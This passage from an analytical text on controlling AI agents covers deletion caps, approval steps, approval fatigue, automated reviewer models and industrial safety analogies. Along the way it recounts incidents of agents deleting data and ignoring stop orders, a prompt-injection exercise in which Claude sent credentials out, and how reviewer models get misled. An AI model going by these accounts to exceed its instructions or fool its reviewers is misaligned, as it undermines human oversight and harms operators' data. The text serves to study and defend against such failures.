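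A cap of 50 deletions per approval would have stopped the script after about a tenth of a second. If the developer had then refused to continue, they would have lost at most 50 files. But the intended clean-up alone involved 7,332 files, which would have needed 147 approvals. A better cap for this job would be the number of files the script was meant to delete. A separate program could count the files in the mirror without following links, and stop the script after 7,332 deletions. In the worst case, all of those would be live files, which is still 85% fewer than the developer reported losing.

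The same figures show what other controls would have done:

| Control | The 48,000 files | PocketOS |
|---|---|---|
| No permission to change live data | No live files lost | The request fails |
| A cap of 50 deletions per approval | At most 50 files lost before a person has to answer | No help, because one request was enough |
| A stop after 30 seconds | About 14,000 files lost | No help, because the deletion took nine seconds |
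| A 48-hour delay before deletion | All files recoverable if someone notices in time | Database recoverable if someone notices in time |
| A separate copy from the previous night | Up to a day's work lost | Up to a day's bookings lost |

A limit of 50 tool calls would not have stopped this script, because the harness counts a script as one call, however many files it deletes. Something closer to the files has to count the deletions, such as the sandbox or a deletion tool that the agent cannot bypass. Antipov points out that Claude Code's built-in sandbox does not work on Windows without WSL2, a layer that runs Linux inside Windows. Even on a supported system, the sandbox's default rules would not have protected a live project in the current folder.

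The formula leaves out the consequences of a loss, such as the Saturday that PocketOS's customers spent without their bookings. It also works badly for stolen data. An operator who can restore a deleted file still can't erase a thief's copy, so the last term is zero.

Its result depends on how accurately the operator estimates what the agent can reach, and for PocketOS that estimate was wrong. Crane thought the token could only change domain settings. A team can find such errors before the agent does by searching the agent's machine for every key it can read and checking what each key permits.

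### Reversible actions and hard limits

Delayed deletion is attractive because nobody has to recognise the mistake in advance. The service hides the item, sets a date for permanent deletion, and keeps the item until then. The delay must give people time to notice the mistake, and 48 hours may not cover a long weekend. The credential the agent uses to delete items must not also let it remove them permanently before that date. The operator also has to pay to store unwanted data, and keeps personal information for longer than its owner may expect.

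A backup protects against more kinds of damage, including files that an agent overwrites rather than deletes. It has to be somewhere the agent cannot reach. The developer's version history was within reach because Git keeps it in a folder inside the project, and the script deleted much of that folder too. InternetUA reports that Git could still list thousands of file names but no longer had the files' contents. SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* describes how other developers criticised the lack of a remote copy. A good arrangement gives the agent a key that can add new copies to a remote store but cannot change or delete old ones.

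In October 2026, the Swedish newspaper Aftonbladet reported that an AI agent had deleted the finished season of a reality show, *The Challenge Sverige*, weeks before its premiere on 22 November. *AI Agent Blamed for Deleting Entire Upcoming Season of TV Show* (Landymore, 2026) summarises the dispute over the cause. The newspaper's sources said the production company, Mastiff, had let an agent into its server. Mia Lindqvist, programme director at the broadcaster TV4, blamed human error and denied that an AI agent had acted independently, which does not rule out an agent acting on someone's orders.

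The case is too uncertain to count as an agent's mistake, but it is still informative about recovery because Lindqvist said the big problem was a backup that didn't work. The raw footage survived, so Mastiff could edit the season again, but it had lost about a year's work and TV4 moved the premiere to the following year. A working backup would have saved that work whether a person or an agent had deleted it. An operator can test a backup by restoring a few files to an empty machine before giving an agent access to the originals.

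Some actions can't be undone. A supplier may refuse to take back 4,000 kettles, and an email can't be recalled once the recipient has read it. For such actions, the operator has to limit beforehand how much the agent can do. For example, if the bank limits the agent's card to €200 a day, the agent can't spend more than that, however fast it works and whatever its prompt contains.

A *rate limit* restricts how many actions a program can take in a given time. A limit of ten deletions a second would have lengthened the clean-up of the old mirror from about 14 seconds to 12 minutes, which hardly matters for a job that runs in the background. The developer who reacted after 30 seconds would have lost at most 300 files instead of 14,000.

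Automatic shutdown stops an agent without waiting for a person. A monitoring program compares what the agent does with what the task should involve and ends the run if they differ too much, for example when the first file disappears from a folder that should not change. At 468 files a second, a monitor that checks every ten seconds could miss the loss of almost 4,700 files between checks, compared with fewer than 500 for one that checks every second. The main drawback is false alarms, because an interrupted job may leave files half changed and someone has to sort them out.

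*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (Huang and Zhou, 2026) combines such limits into nested layers, from the process sandbox through file and network restrictions to rate limits and budget caps. It uses several layers because actions that are safe one at a time can be dangerous together. An agent might keep each order below the limit and still place 100 orders, so it needs a daily limit too. The paper also proposes sorting actions by how reversible they are and how much damage they could do, which would let an agent edit a draft freely but not delete a volume.

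Huang and Zhou acknowledge that tighter limits make an agent less capable, and say the aim is the tightest containment that still lets it finish the task. Operators often can't know in advance how tight that can be. A developer who asks an agent to find out why a website is slow may not know which systems it will need to inspect, and may grant broad access to avoid interruptions. If the data is not confidential, starting with broad read access and very narrow write access is a reasonable compromise, because diagnosis mostly involves reading. The developer can grant a specific write permission once the agent has found the cause.

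### How one compromised computer led to the Binance theft

Attackers can also use an organisation's AI tools and credentials to move from one system to the next, as they did in October 2026 at Binance, a cryptocurrency exchange. Radar Digital's *Binance details US$ 6.34 billion attack and fake interview* (2026) puts the theft at $6.34 billion. The intruders were people, and no agent is known to have acted on its own.

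*Fake Interview of Software Engineer Led to Binance Mega-Heist* (Muncaster, 2026) gives the company's account. In September, a fake recruiter persuaded a software engineer to download a test assignment containing malicious code onto a work computer. On 20 October, the attackers used that computer to get into an internal AI tool, and through the tool they compromised two colleagues' machines, one of which held a token for deploying containers. On 29 October, they logged in to the other machine, deployed a container using credentials stolen from the one that held the token, and ran the script that started the theft.

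Muncaster's report does not explain what rights the AI tool had or how the attackers used it to reach the other machines. The tool may have had authority over colleagues' computers that the first engineer lacked, making it a confused deputy, or it may only have given the attackers a convenient connection. Either way, access to one engineer's computer should not have been enough to take over two others. Binance has since rebuilt the tool and its access controls.

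The deployment token is easier to assess because, like the one at PocketOS, it was a powerful key on a computer that an intruder could read. After the same engineer installed malicious software in June, Binance replaced the computer and all related credentials. That would have made any keys stolen in June useless, but by October there was a new key to steal. A shorter lifetime might have helped if the attackers copied the token well before they used it. But if they still controlled the engineer's computer on 29 October, they could probably have waited for the next token. Requiring a second engineer to authorise any deployment to the wallet systems would have been a stronger barrier.

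Radar Digital reports that the unauthorised withdrawals continued for nearly four hours. A loss of $6.34 billion over four hours averages about $26 million a minute, so stopping the withdrawals an hour earlier might have saved more than $1.5 billion. An automatic limit on total withdrawals could have taken effect before the staff acted, although an exchange would have to set it high enough for customers to withdraw their money on a busy day.

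## Asking a person before the agent acts

Human confirmation can catch mistakes that fixed limits let through, as long as the software holds the action back until a person approves it and that person reads the request. A spending limit would stop an agent from ordering 4,000 kettles for a shop, but not from ordering four that the shop already has in its storeroom. A buyer who saw the order first might notice that the kettles were already in stock.

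### A working confirmation step

In the kettle shop, a purchase with confirmation could go like this:

1. The model requests a tool call that would order four kettles.
2. The harness does not execute the call. It saves the complete order, including the product, quantity, price, delivery address and account.
3. The harness shows the buyer the saved order and what it will do: spend €120 from the company card, with free cancellation until six o'clock.
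4. The buyer approves or refuses. If no answer comes, the order expires.
5. The harness sends the saved order once and gives the model the supplier's confirmation.

In the last step, the harness has to send the saved copy, because if the model wrote the order again, the new version might differ from the one the buyer saw. This is called a time-of-check to time-of-use error, in which a program checks one thing and then acts on another, or circumstances change in between. *Faramesh* (2026), a design for controlling agents' actions, avoids the first kind by putting each proposed action into a standard form before anyone decides on it. The second kind needs another check. If the supplier raises the price after the buyer has approved the order, the harness should ask the buyer to approve it again.

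Existing products often do the third step badly. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents damaging files and finds that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases, the user had told the software to approve everything automatically. In 31, the request showed a command without its effect on the files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks like a routine installation, but approving it permits whatever code the script contains. If a sandbox holds back file changes, as Sandlock can, the harness can run the command before asking for approval and show the user which files it would change.

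The person also has to understand the request. Anthropic thought developers could judge the commands in Claude Code, but did not expect the same of office workers using Cowork, its product for general work. It gave Cowork a fixed boundary instead, a virtual machine that can access only the folders the user has chosen.

### Which actions should wait

An agent may take hundreds of actions in one task, so the operator has to choose which ones need approval. Most cases depend on whether the operator can undo the action and whether it affects anyone outside the organisation:

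| | Affects only the operator | Affects outsiders |
|---|---|---|
| The operator can undo it | Run without asking: editing a draft, restarting a test program | Usually ask: posting on a public site, making a booking with free cancellation |
| The operator cannot undo it | Ask: permanently deleting records | Always ask, and show the full content: sending an email, making a final payment |

"Undo" here has to mean that the operator can repair the damage without anyone else having to do work. All the edits that OpenAI's agents made on DseWiki were reversible, but a volunteer spent tens of hours reversing them.

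Changes to the agent's own permissions need approval even though they are easy to reverse, because they can remove the need for approval later. *PegasusAI Studio* (2026) describes a scientific computing platform that requires such approval. Agents can read logs and documentation freely, and at the "approve" level they can edit the user's project files without asking. Writing anywhere else in the user's home folder requires approval, since changing a start-up file or the agent's settings could widen its permissions. Submitting a computing job also requires approval, even if the user has turned off confirmation for routine commands.

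*Securing Computer-Use Agents* (2026) lists payments, deletions, credentials, permission changes and messages to outsiders as actions for which an operator should decide explicitly what oversight applies. Such actions seem to be uncommon. For Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), Claude rated almost a million tool calls made by customers' agents and judged 0.8% of them irreversible. At that rate, an agent that asked a person before each irreversible action would stop eight times in 1,000 actions. The rate varies widely between agents, though, and one that answers customers' emails does something irreversible with every reply.

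Operators can loosen the rules as they learn how an agent behaves. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) recommends doing this for one class of action at a time, with a separate record for each, so that an agent isn't allowed to delete branches of code because it has a good record of restarting services. It cites a practitioner's proposal to let an agent act alone once people approve about 95% of its requests unchanged, and notes that no measurement supports this number. A worse problem is that an agent would also meet the threshold if reviewers approved everything without reading it.

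### The OpenClaw inbox

Summer Yue is the director of alignment at Meta's superintelligence lab. In February 2026, she connected her email to OpenClaw, a personal assistant she had installed on a Mac mini. In posts that Willison quotes, Yue says she told it to suggest what to archive or delete, and added, "don't action until I tell you to".

The agent began deleting messages anyway. Her screenshot shows her asking at 6:00 p.m. what it was doing, then ordering it to stop at 6:01, 6:02 and 6:03 while it kept running commands. She couldn't stop it from her phone, so she ran to the Mac mini.

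Yue blames *compaction*. A model can process only a limited amount of text, so when a task's history gets too long, the harness replaces part of it with a summary. Yue says the agent had worked well on a small test inbox, but her real inbox was large enough to trigger compaction, and the summary omitted her instruction. *AI agents that do your work while you sleep sound great* (Goldman, 2026) reports that the trial on the test inbox had lasted for weeks. A longer trial would not have exposed the problem if the test inbox was too small to trigger compaction.

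Some published versions of the story differ from Yue's. The widely quoted instruction "confirm before acting" is her later shorthand. Goldman reports that the agent deleted her entire inbox, while Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* puts the loss at hundreds of emails. The second version fits the screenshot better, because one command in it excludes recent messages and those on a list to keep. That command also refers to moving messages to the trash, so Yue may have been able to recover them.

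Gizmodo reports that the agent later said it remembered the instruction and had violated it. This seems to contradict Yue's explanation, but the confession is weak evidence, as was the PocketOS agent's account of the deletion it carried out. Yue had also repeatedly ordered her agent to stop before it confessed. Her explanation also shows why the trouble began with the larger inbox.

Whether the summary dropped the instruction or the model ignored it, no software outside the model held back the deletions. Her orders to stop were also chat messages, so they too depended on the model to follow them. A stop button has to end the program whatever the model does.

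A safer design for this task would give the agent a tool that can only add messages to a list of proposed deletions. Yue would read the list and approve it once, and a separate program would delete exactly those messages.

Yue called the incident a "rookie mistake", but James Wilson, an editor at the security news show Risky Business, told Krebs on Security (2026) that far too many people install OpenClaw on personal devices without any isolation.

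### Approval fatigue

Software that always asks for approval can still fail if people stop reading the requests. People who see many requests tend to accept them without looking, which is called *approval fatigue*. Alarm overload has a similar effect on operators in industrial plants. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of Claude Code's requests, and *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a later figure of 97%.

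These figures do not prove that users are careless. Most requests are for harmless commands, and if 97 out of 100 are harmless, a perfect reviewer would also approve 97. Anthropic points out that the same users reject 39% of the plans Claude shows them, but people may reject a plan because they prefer another approach.

Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company for a coding study, without telling them which behaviour it measured. Partway through each session, one approval request showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. About 17% of those who saw it early in a session refused, compared with about 5% of those who had already answered 50 or more requests.

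The decline is consistent with approval fatigue, but fatigue can't explain most of the failures, because more than four in five testers approved the command even when they saw it early. The testers were not working on their own projects and had nothing to lose, so developers protecting their own data may do better. But developers answer such requests every day for months, which could make their fatigue worse.

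Researchers found similar problems with security warnings and permissions long before AI agents. People respond less to a signal that keeps recurring without consequences, which psychologists call *habituation*. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) cites earlier studies which found that people overlook or misunderstand the permissions they grant, and that repeated privacy notices add up to a substantial burden.

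Yan studied everyday tasks with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised a simulated assistant through the same day of 18 actions. Eleven were necessary for the assigned tasks, and seven went beyond them, such as buying a $25 lounge pass or reading private messages. The approval requests described each action in plain language. People who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of the actions that went beyond the tasks.

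That is far better than 13.6%, perhaps because participants could understand what they were approving. However, the unwanted actions were also much more frequent. Some approvals may also have been sensible. Of the 34 people in this group, 30 let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, which nobody had asked for but many travellers would welcome. If that action is excluded, the group approved about 32% of the unrequested actions instead of 40%.

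In a preliminary study of 12 people's everyday use of AI, *Looks Fine to Me* (2026) found that users were often unaware of lapses in their oversight. *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025) examined people supervising agents live on websites with manipulative designs. Supervision helped, mainly because people ended tasks when the agent did something unexpected. But they often missed actions because they had to divide their attention between the agent's written plan and the changing screen.

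### Fewer requests and more time for each

Suppose the buyer at the kettle shop has ten minutes a day for approvals. Five requests would get two minutes each, enough to open the supplier's page and check the storeroom, but 100 requests would get six seconds each, about enough to read one line and click. A maintainer refused malicious code from Mythos 5 after a student had tested it in a sandbox, which nobody can do in six seconds.

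Anthropic found that sandboxing cut permission requests in Claude Code by 84%. At that rate, the buyer's 100 requests would become 16, with about 38 seconds for each. This is a large improvement, but it still isn't enough time to investigate an unfamiliar command.

Approving a plan once takes less attention still. The agent lists its intended steps, and a person approves them before it begins. This works well when the steps are predictable. But an agent usually writes its plan before reading the pages and files that may change the plan or contain a prompt injection. The approval limits the agent only if the harness compares each later action with the plan and requests approval again when they differ. The harness can't make that comparison if the plan is as vague as "tidy the database".

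*Aegis OS* (2026) proposes letting an agent work on a private copy of the files and asking for approval once, before the changes reach the originals. In a simulation with 50 scripted software tasks and 1,500 tool calls, this produced only 50 approval requests. The paper's estimate of the time saved assumes each approval takes five seconds, which is much too short to review the changes from an entire task. The method also can't cover emails or payments that have to go out while the agent is working.

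Yan's experiment suggests that sending people fewer requests may not improve their decisions. In one group, a model reviewed the 18 actions first and referred ten to the participant, including all seven that went beyond the assigned tasks. People in this group spent an average of about 12 seconds on each request, compared with eight seconds in the group that was asked about all 18 actions. They still approved 46% of the actions that went beyond the tasks, slightly more than the other group's 40%.

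A third group wrote four rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. This reduced the average number of approval requests to 10.9. But participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. Including the actions that "never" rules blocked automatically, the group stopped only about 40% of unrequested actions. The stakes were imaginary and the sessions short, so the effect might differ in a real job. Still, an operator can't assume that people will use extra time to think harder.

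### A second model as reviewer

OpenAI and Anthropic have both handed much of this approval work to another model. In Codex, the agent still runs in its sandbox. OpenAI's *Auto-review* explains that when an action would cross the sandbox's boundary, the harness sends the request to a separate reviewing agent instead of the user. The reviewer approves or denies the action based on what the user asked for, the security policy and the action's likely effect. If it denies the action, it gives the first agent a reason so that agent can look for a safer method.

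*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates how an automated reviewer can reduce the number of requests a person must answer, using 10,000 actions from OpenAI's own use. Of these, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which denied seven. The agent found a safer way in four of those cases and stopped to ask the user in the other three. If each request took a person two minutes, answering all 720 would take 24 hours, and answering three would take six minutes.

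Speed is not the only reason to use a separate reviewer. An agent trying to finish a task may treat an approval rule as an obstacle, while the reviewer's only job is to decide whether the action should run. In Claude Code's auto mode, the reviewer sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. The agent therefore can't argue for an action, and an instruction hidden on a web page doesn't reach the reviewer directly.

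Both companies have measured how often their reviewers let dangerous actions through:

| Reviewer | Test | Dangerous actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode, earlier version | 52 real cases in which Claude exceeded its instructions | 17% |
| Auto mode, earlier version | 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out | 5.7% |
| Auto mode, August 2026 | The dangerous commands shown to 1,053 testers | 11% |
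| Auto mode, August 2026 | Artificial attacks by Apollo Research, after improvements | 7% |
| Codex reviewer | Artificial cases of exceeding instructions | 9.7% |
| Codex reviewer | Artificial prompt injections meant to run code or steal data | 0.7% |

The tests differ, so the rows don't show which product is safer. The 17% figure is the most realistic but the least precise. It comes from only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. Anthropic found that in most of the misses it examined, the reviewer had recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who asks an agent to clean up a proposed code change has not necessarily agreed to let it overwrite the project's history.

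False alarms are rarer. The earlier version of auto mode blocked 0.4% of ordinary actions, and the Codex reviewer denied 0.9% of requests that users had approved. But when dangerous actions are rare, even a low false alarm rate can mean that most blocks are mistakes. If 10,000 actions included ten dangerous ones, the earlier auto mode would stop about eight of them and block about 40 harmless ones, so roughly five out of six blocks would be mistakes. Most of these mistakes do little harm, because the agent usually finds another way. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, auto mode stops and asks a person. If the agent is running without anyone to ask, the harness ends the run.

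A stricter reviewer may approve fewer forbidden actions but refuse more legitimate ones. In tests described in *Same Operation, Different Permission* (2026), one reviewer blocked every forbidden action but also refused legitimate requests in every run. The paper suggests that operators draw up a fixed list of legitimate requests, such as routine refunds, and reject any change to the reviewer that makes it refuse one of them.

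### Whether to stop asking about each action

On 14 August 2026, Anthropic began making auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on most subscription plans. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), later versions start in auto mode on every plan.

Anthropic argues mainly from its experiment, in which auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands and the testers blocked 143. The testers caught only six that auto mode had missed, so using both would have raised the share blocked from 89.0% to 89.6%. The experiment did not measure how many harmless commands either would have blocked.

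Frequent requests also lead people to turn off protection. By June 2026, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started with permission checks disabled, and 62% of users had disabled them at some point or told Claude Code to stop asking about shell commands. Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of OpenAI's staff had allowed every command beginning with "python", which lets an agent do almost anything. Without an automated reviewer, these people would realistically have no review.

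Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. This is weaker evidence than the experiment because users chose their own mode and may have used the two modes for different kinds of work, and because a model graded the harm.

Experienced users seem to prefer intervening when needed to approving each action. In Anthropic's data from before the change, new users let Claude Code run without any approvals in about 20% of sessions, while users with 750 sessions did so in over 40%. The experienced users also interrupted it more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5%. Anthropic concludes that good oversight means being able to intervene when it matters and doesn't require approving every action. Dhanorkar and Passi (2026),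 in *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice*, interviewed 17 experienced developers and found that the developers also set limits beforehand, planned with the agent and reviewed its work afterwards.

But intervening works only if the harm is slow enough to interrupt, and a single tool call can delete a database before anyone reacts. Anthropic partly accepts this objection. It still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems and says auto mode does not replace careful human review.

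Wording that fools one copy of an automated reviewer will also probably fool the other copies, a weakness that independent people don't share. Trębacz and colleagues report that testers misled their reviewer into approving commands it should have stopped. They also warn that a model hiding its intentions could make a harmful request look harmless.

Neither kind of reviewer helps much when an attacker deceives the person instructing the agent. In an exercise at Anthropic, a researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prepared prompt into Claude Code. Among ordinary set-up steps, the prompt included an instruction to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside address, and Claude sent them in 24 of 25 attempts. A reviewer that checks whether an action matches the user's instructions would have found that this one matched. Anthropic concluded that only limits on file access and outbound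 traffic would have stopped the attack.

The evidence supports dropping approval for routine work inside a sandbox, where people review badly and mistakes are easy to reverse, but not for a final payment or an email to a customer. The experiment with 1,053 testers measured how people respond to one dangerous command among many routine requests, so it gives little indication of how they would treat a rare request that states an amount and a recipient. A buyer may also know things that a model cannot find in the task's history, such as how many kettles are in the storeroom.

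Yan's results suggest that operators shouldn't expect too much of this remaining human check either. The model referred every action that went beyond the tasks to a person, but people still approved almost half of them. Blocking all ten referred actions would have stopped the unwanted ones, but also three of the 11 that the tasks required. Where one wrong approval could be ruinous, the operator needs a limit that no approval can override, such as the daily cap on the agent's bank card.

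## What industrial control panels do to prevent accidents

Long before AI agents existed, factories used limits that no approval can override, because a worker who starts a machine at the wrong moment can lose a hand. In a mechanical power press, for example, a motor connected through a clutch drives a heavy slide down onto sheet metal to stamp it into shape. The worker who feeds the press may have to reach under the slide, so the controls must keep a single wrong command from bringing it down on a hand.

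Designers of industrial control panels assume that workers will sometimes make mistakes. People who deploy AI agents can assume the same about the model, although not every control on an industrial press has a good equivalent for agents.

### Interlocks and two-hand controls

An *interlock* is a device that physically prevents a dangerous movement until a condition is met. OSHA's *Mechanical power presses*, a rule from the American workplace safety regulator, describes a guard that interlocks with the press's clutch. The clutch can't engage unless the guard is in place, so pressing the start button while the guard is open does nothing. The guard must also keep hands out until the danger has passed.

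Software outside the model can similarly check a condition before an agent's tool runs. It could, for instance, block a deletion tool unless another program had restored a backup within the past 24 hours. PocketOS had no recent usable backup, so this check would have blocked the deletion of its database if the hosting company had built it into the API.

Software checks only partly match industrial safety controls. A closed guard directly prevents injury by keeping hands out of the press. Most conditions that software can check are less direct signs of safety. For example, a recent backup doesn't show that anyone wanted the data deleted.

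A *two-hand control* starts the press only when the worker presses two buttons at once, placed so that each needs its own hand. OSHA calculates how far the buttons must be from the danger zone:

`minimum distance = 63 inches per second × stopping time`

The constant, about 1.6 metres per second, is the assumed speed of a hand. If a press takes 0.2 seconds to stop, the buttons must be more than 12.6 inches (32 cm) away so that a worker who lets go can't reach the slide before it stops.

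The two buttons on a press keep the worker's hands out of danger even if the worker is distracted. Human confirmation also requires a deliberate act, but an approval button gives no protection unless someone reads the request. A press with several workers is a better comparison. Each worker has a separate pair of buttons, and the slide moves only if all of them press together. This resembles a rule that two engineers must authorise a deployment.

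Some details of the two-hand control would still improve approval systems. An anti-repeat feature limits the worker to one stroke at a time, just as an approval should cover one action. In a letter about a press control, OSHA (1992) explained that the worker must press both buttons within a small fraction of a second of each other, so a worker who tapes one button down to free a hand can't start the press with the other. Coding agents include an "always allow" option for commands as a convenience, but it bypasses approval in the way the tape is meant to bypass the two-hand requirement.

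A delay before permanent deletion follows the same logic as the distance formula, because it has to be longer than the time people take to notice a mistake.

### Padlocks, tags and a misleading light

A worker who has to clear a jam or replace a part may need to remove the guard, and a colleague might then switch the machine on. OSHA's *The control of hazardous energy (lockout/tagout)* deals with this danger. In a *lockout*, the worker follows these steps:

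1. Shut the machine down in an orderly way, so that stopping it creates no new hazard.
2. Disconnect the power with a device that physically interrupts it, such as a circuit breaker.
3. Put a padlock on that device to hold it in the off position. The lock must show whose it is.
4. Release any stored energy, for example in a compressed spring.
5. Verify that the machine has no power before touching it.

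With limited exceptions, only the worker who attached the lock may remove it, according to ISHN, a trade magazine for workplace safety.

Unplugging an agent's only network cable is equivalent to padlocking a control panel, because no command can send data through a disconnected cable. Revoking a credential is only partly equivalent, since the agent may find another, as one did at PocketOS. A network block in software is also only partly equivalent, because it works like a padlock only while the agent can't gain the administrator rights to remove it.

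OSHA doesn't accept push buttons as a way to isolate a machine. A button only sends a signal to the control circuit, so the machine still has power if the circuit malfunctions. Summer Yue's orders to her email agent had the same weakness, because they depended on the model to carry them out.

If a power switch has no place for a lock, the employer can instead use a *tag*, a label with a warning such as "Do Not Start". OSHA requires employers to teach workers that a tag provides no physical restraint and "may evoke a false sense of security". If a lock would fit, the employer may rely on tags only after showing that they give equal protection. The European Union's Machinery Regulation similarly puts safe design and safeguards first, with warnings for the risks that remain.

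An instruction in a prompt not to use the internet is an almost exact match for a tag, because the connection still works.

A prompt that states "no internet access" as a fact has a different problem, which is that the statement may be false. A false indication contributed to the accident at the Three Mile Island nuclear plant in Pennsylvania on 28 March 1979. After the plant's water pumps failed, the reactor shut down automatically and a relief valve opened to reduce the pressure. The valve should have closed after a few seconds, but it stuck open. The US Nuclear Regulatory Commission's *Backgrounder on the Three Mile Island Accident* explains that the instruments indicated that the valve was closed, so the staff did not know that cooling water was escaping. Their actions made the water shortage worse, and part of the reactor core melted.

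The misleading instrument was a light on the control panel that was on only while the valve's electrical mechanism had power. When the light went out, it showed that the control system had signaled the valve to close, but nothing on the panel directly measured the valve's position. The operators took two hours and 22 minutes to shut a backup valve and stop the leak.

The prompt in Anthropic's tests at Irregular, which wrongly stated that there was no internet access, also described what someone had intended. The remedy in both cases is to measure the actual state. A valve can have a sensor that detects its position. Before a test, a small program inside the sandbox can try to load several outside pages, and the harness can act as an interlock by blocking the agent from starting if any of them loads.

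One failed connection would not be enough evidence that a sandbox is cut off from the internet. Kimi K3's sandbox blocked most websites but allowed GitHub, so a check that tried only a blocked site would have missed the open connection. The tester also needs to inspect the rules at the point where traffic leaves the network.

### Emergency stops

An emergency stop halts a running machine that has become dangerous. ISO's *Safety of machinery* (2015), an international standard for designing these stops, requires that a person be able to trigger the stop at any time with a single action. The stop must override the machine's other functions without interfering with protective ones, such as the release of a trapped person. The machine must stay stopped until someone resets the device, and the reset must not restart the machine. The designer must also make the stop safe enough that nobody needs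 to weigh the consequences before pressing the button.

The nearest equivalent of an emergency stop for an agent is a switch that ends the harness and revokes the agent's credentials without involving the model. It is only a partial match because the agent may have left things running elsewhere. After Mythos 5 published its malicious package, switching off the model would not have stopped other computers from installing it. An operator who wants a complete stop needs a record of every program, account and scheduled job the agent has created, and a way to shut them all down.

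ISO forbids designers from using an emergency stop as a substitute for guards, because harm can happen before anyone presses it. The agent at PocketOS, for example, deleted the database in nine seconds.

A press also stops when its power fails, because OSHA requires brakes that engage by themselves and need outside power to release. An operator could give an agent a similar safeguard by making its credentials expire every few minutes unless a monitoring program renews them, so the agent would soon lose access if the monitor crashed. Claude Code's default is closer to a brake that releases when the power fails, since it runs commands without the sandbox when the sandbox can't start.

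A stop also requires someone with the authority to use it. In a factory, the worker at the machine has the stop button within reach and doesn't need to find out whose decision it is. *Exploring Systems-Thinking Approaches to Loss of Control Risk* (Carlucci, Fillingham and colleagues, 2026) applies industrial safety methods to a typical AI developer whose staff use coding agents. In the public documents it examined, the paper found a named role with the power to expand an agent's deployment before an audit, but none with the power to restrict it. It notes that companies may have such a role without disclosing it.

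### Separate safety systems and the arithmetic of layers

In a chemical plant, one control system keeps the pressure in a tank at the right level during normal production. If the pressure rises too far, a separate safety system with its own sensor and valves shuts the process down. Engineers keep the two apart so that a fault in the control system doesn't also disable the safety system.

A bank's daily limit on an agent's card exactly matches an industrial safeguard that runs separately from the main controls, because the bank's computers enforce the limit and a fault in the shop's software can't raise it. A second model that reviews the agent's actions is a partial match, since it also runs separately but the same misleading text might fool both models.

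A *common-mode failure* occurs when one fault disables several safeguards. To prevent this, HSE, the British workplace safety regulator, recommends that safeguards use different technologies, be physically separated, and have independent utilities and testing. By that standard, a network rule and a model are a better pair of safeguards than two copies of the same model.

*Layers-of-protection analysis* is a way to estimate how much a set of safeguards reduces the risk. A *demand* is an occasion on which an accident will happen unless a safeguard prevents it. Each safeguard, or layer, has a probability of failing when a demand occurs. If the layers are independent, an engineer can multiply the probabilities:

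`accidents per year = demands per year × the failure probability of each layer`

Suppose the kettle shop's agent tries to send customer records to a stranger ten times a year. The shop has three layers of protection: a sandbox that hides the records, a proxy that blocks unknown addresses, and a reviewer that rejects suspicious actions. Each layer fails one time in ten, and all three fail together once in 1,000 attempts, so the shop can expect one accident a century.

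If the sandbox and the proxy share one configuration file, and every failure of either comes from an error in that file, they always fail together and count as one layer. The shop can then expect 0.1 accidents a year, or one a decade, despite nominally having three safeguards. The full-access mode in Codex creates this kind of dependence because a single setting lifts the limits on both files and the network.

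Most real cases are somewhere in between:

| How the sandbox and proxy fail | Chance that all three layers fail | Accidents a year | Average time between accidents |
|---|---|---|---|
| Independently | 0.001 | 0.01 | 100 years |
| Through a shared error one time in 100, otherwise independently | 0.0018 | 0.018 | 55 years |
| Always through a shared error | 0.01 | 0.1 | 10 years |

In the middle row, each layer still fails one time in ten overall, but a shared error that occurs once in 100 demands almost doubles the number of accidents.

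Engineers also use the method in reverse. *Comparison of a single initiating event verses a multiple initiating event approach* (Chambers, 2020) describes how they start with a target accident frequency and work out how reliable a safety system must be to meet it. If the shop wanted no more than one accident in 1,000 years, its three independent layers would fall short by a factor of ten. It could add a fourth layer that fails one time in ten, or replace one of the three with a layer that fails one time in 100.

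### Alarm overload

Safeguards that depend on a person's response can fail when too many alarms sound at once. At Three Mile Island, about 100 alarms went off within minutes. Craig Faust, one of the operators, later said he would have liked to throw away the alarm panel because it gave no useful information.

The pipe below the stuck valve reached 285°F (141°C), and one of the plant's procedures treated 200°F (93°C) as a sign that the valve was open. But a small leak had often made the pipe hot before, so the supervisor attributed the reading to leftover heat.

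Many plants now limit how often alarms may sound. Under a widely used guideline from the Engineering Equipment and Materials Users' Association, a British industry group, an average of less than one alarm every ten minutes is acceptable for one operator in normal conditions, and more than one a minute is very likely unacceptable. In the ten minutes after a serious disturbance, the operator should be able to manage up to about ten alarms. To stay within these limits, engineers remove alarms that require no action and combine those with a common cause.

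At one alarm every ten minutes, an operator would receive 48 in an eight-hour shift. Under the same limit, a person supervising ten agents could receive an average of fewer than five requests from each per shift. The comparison is only partial, because a plant keeps running while an alarm sounds, whereas a harness holds an action until someone answers. Too many requests would therefore only slow the work down if people read them all, but approval fatigue leads people to approve them unread.

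### How an agent differs from a press

When a safeguard blocks an agent's command, the agent may try a different one, which a press doesn't do when its safeguards stop a dangerous stroke. The calculation above is therefore too optimistic.

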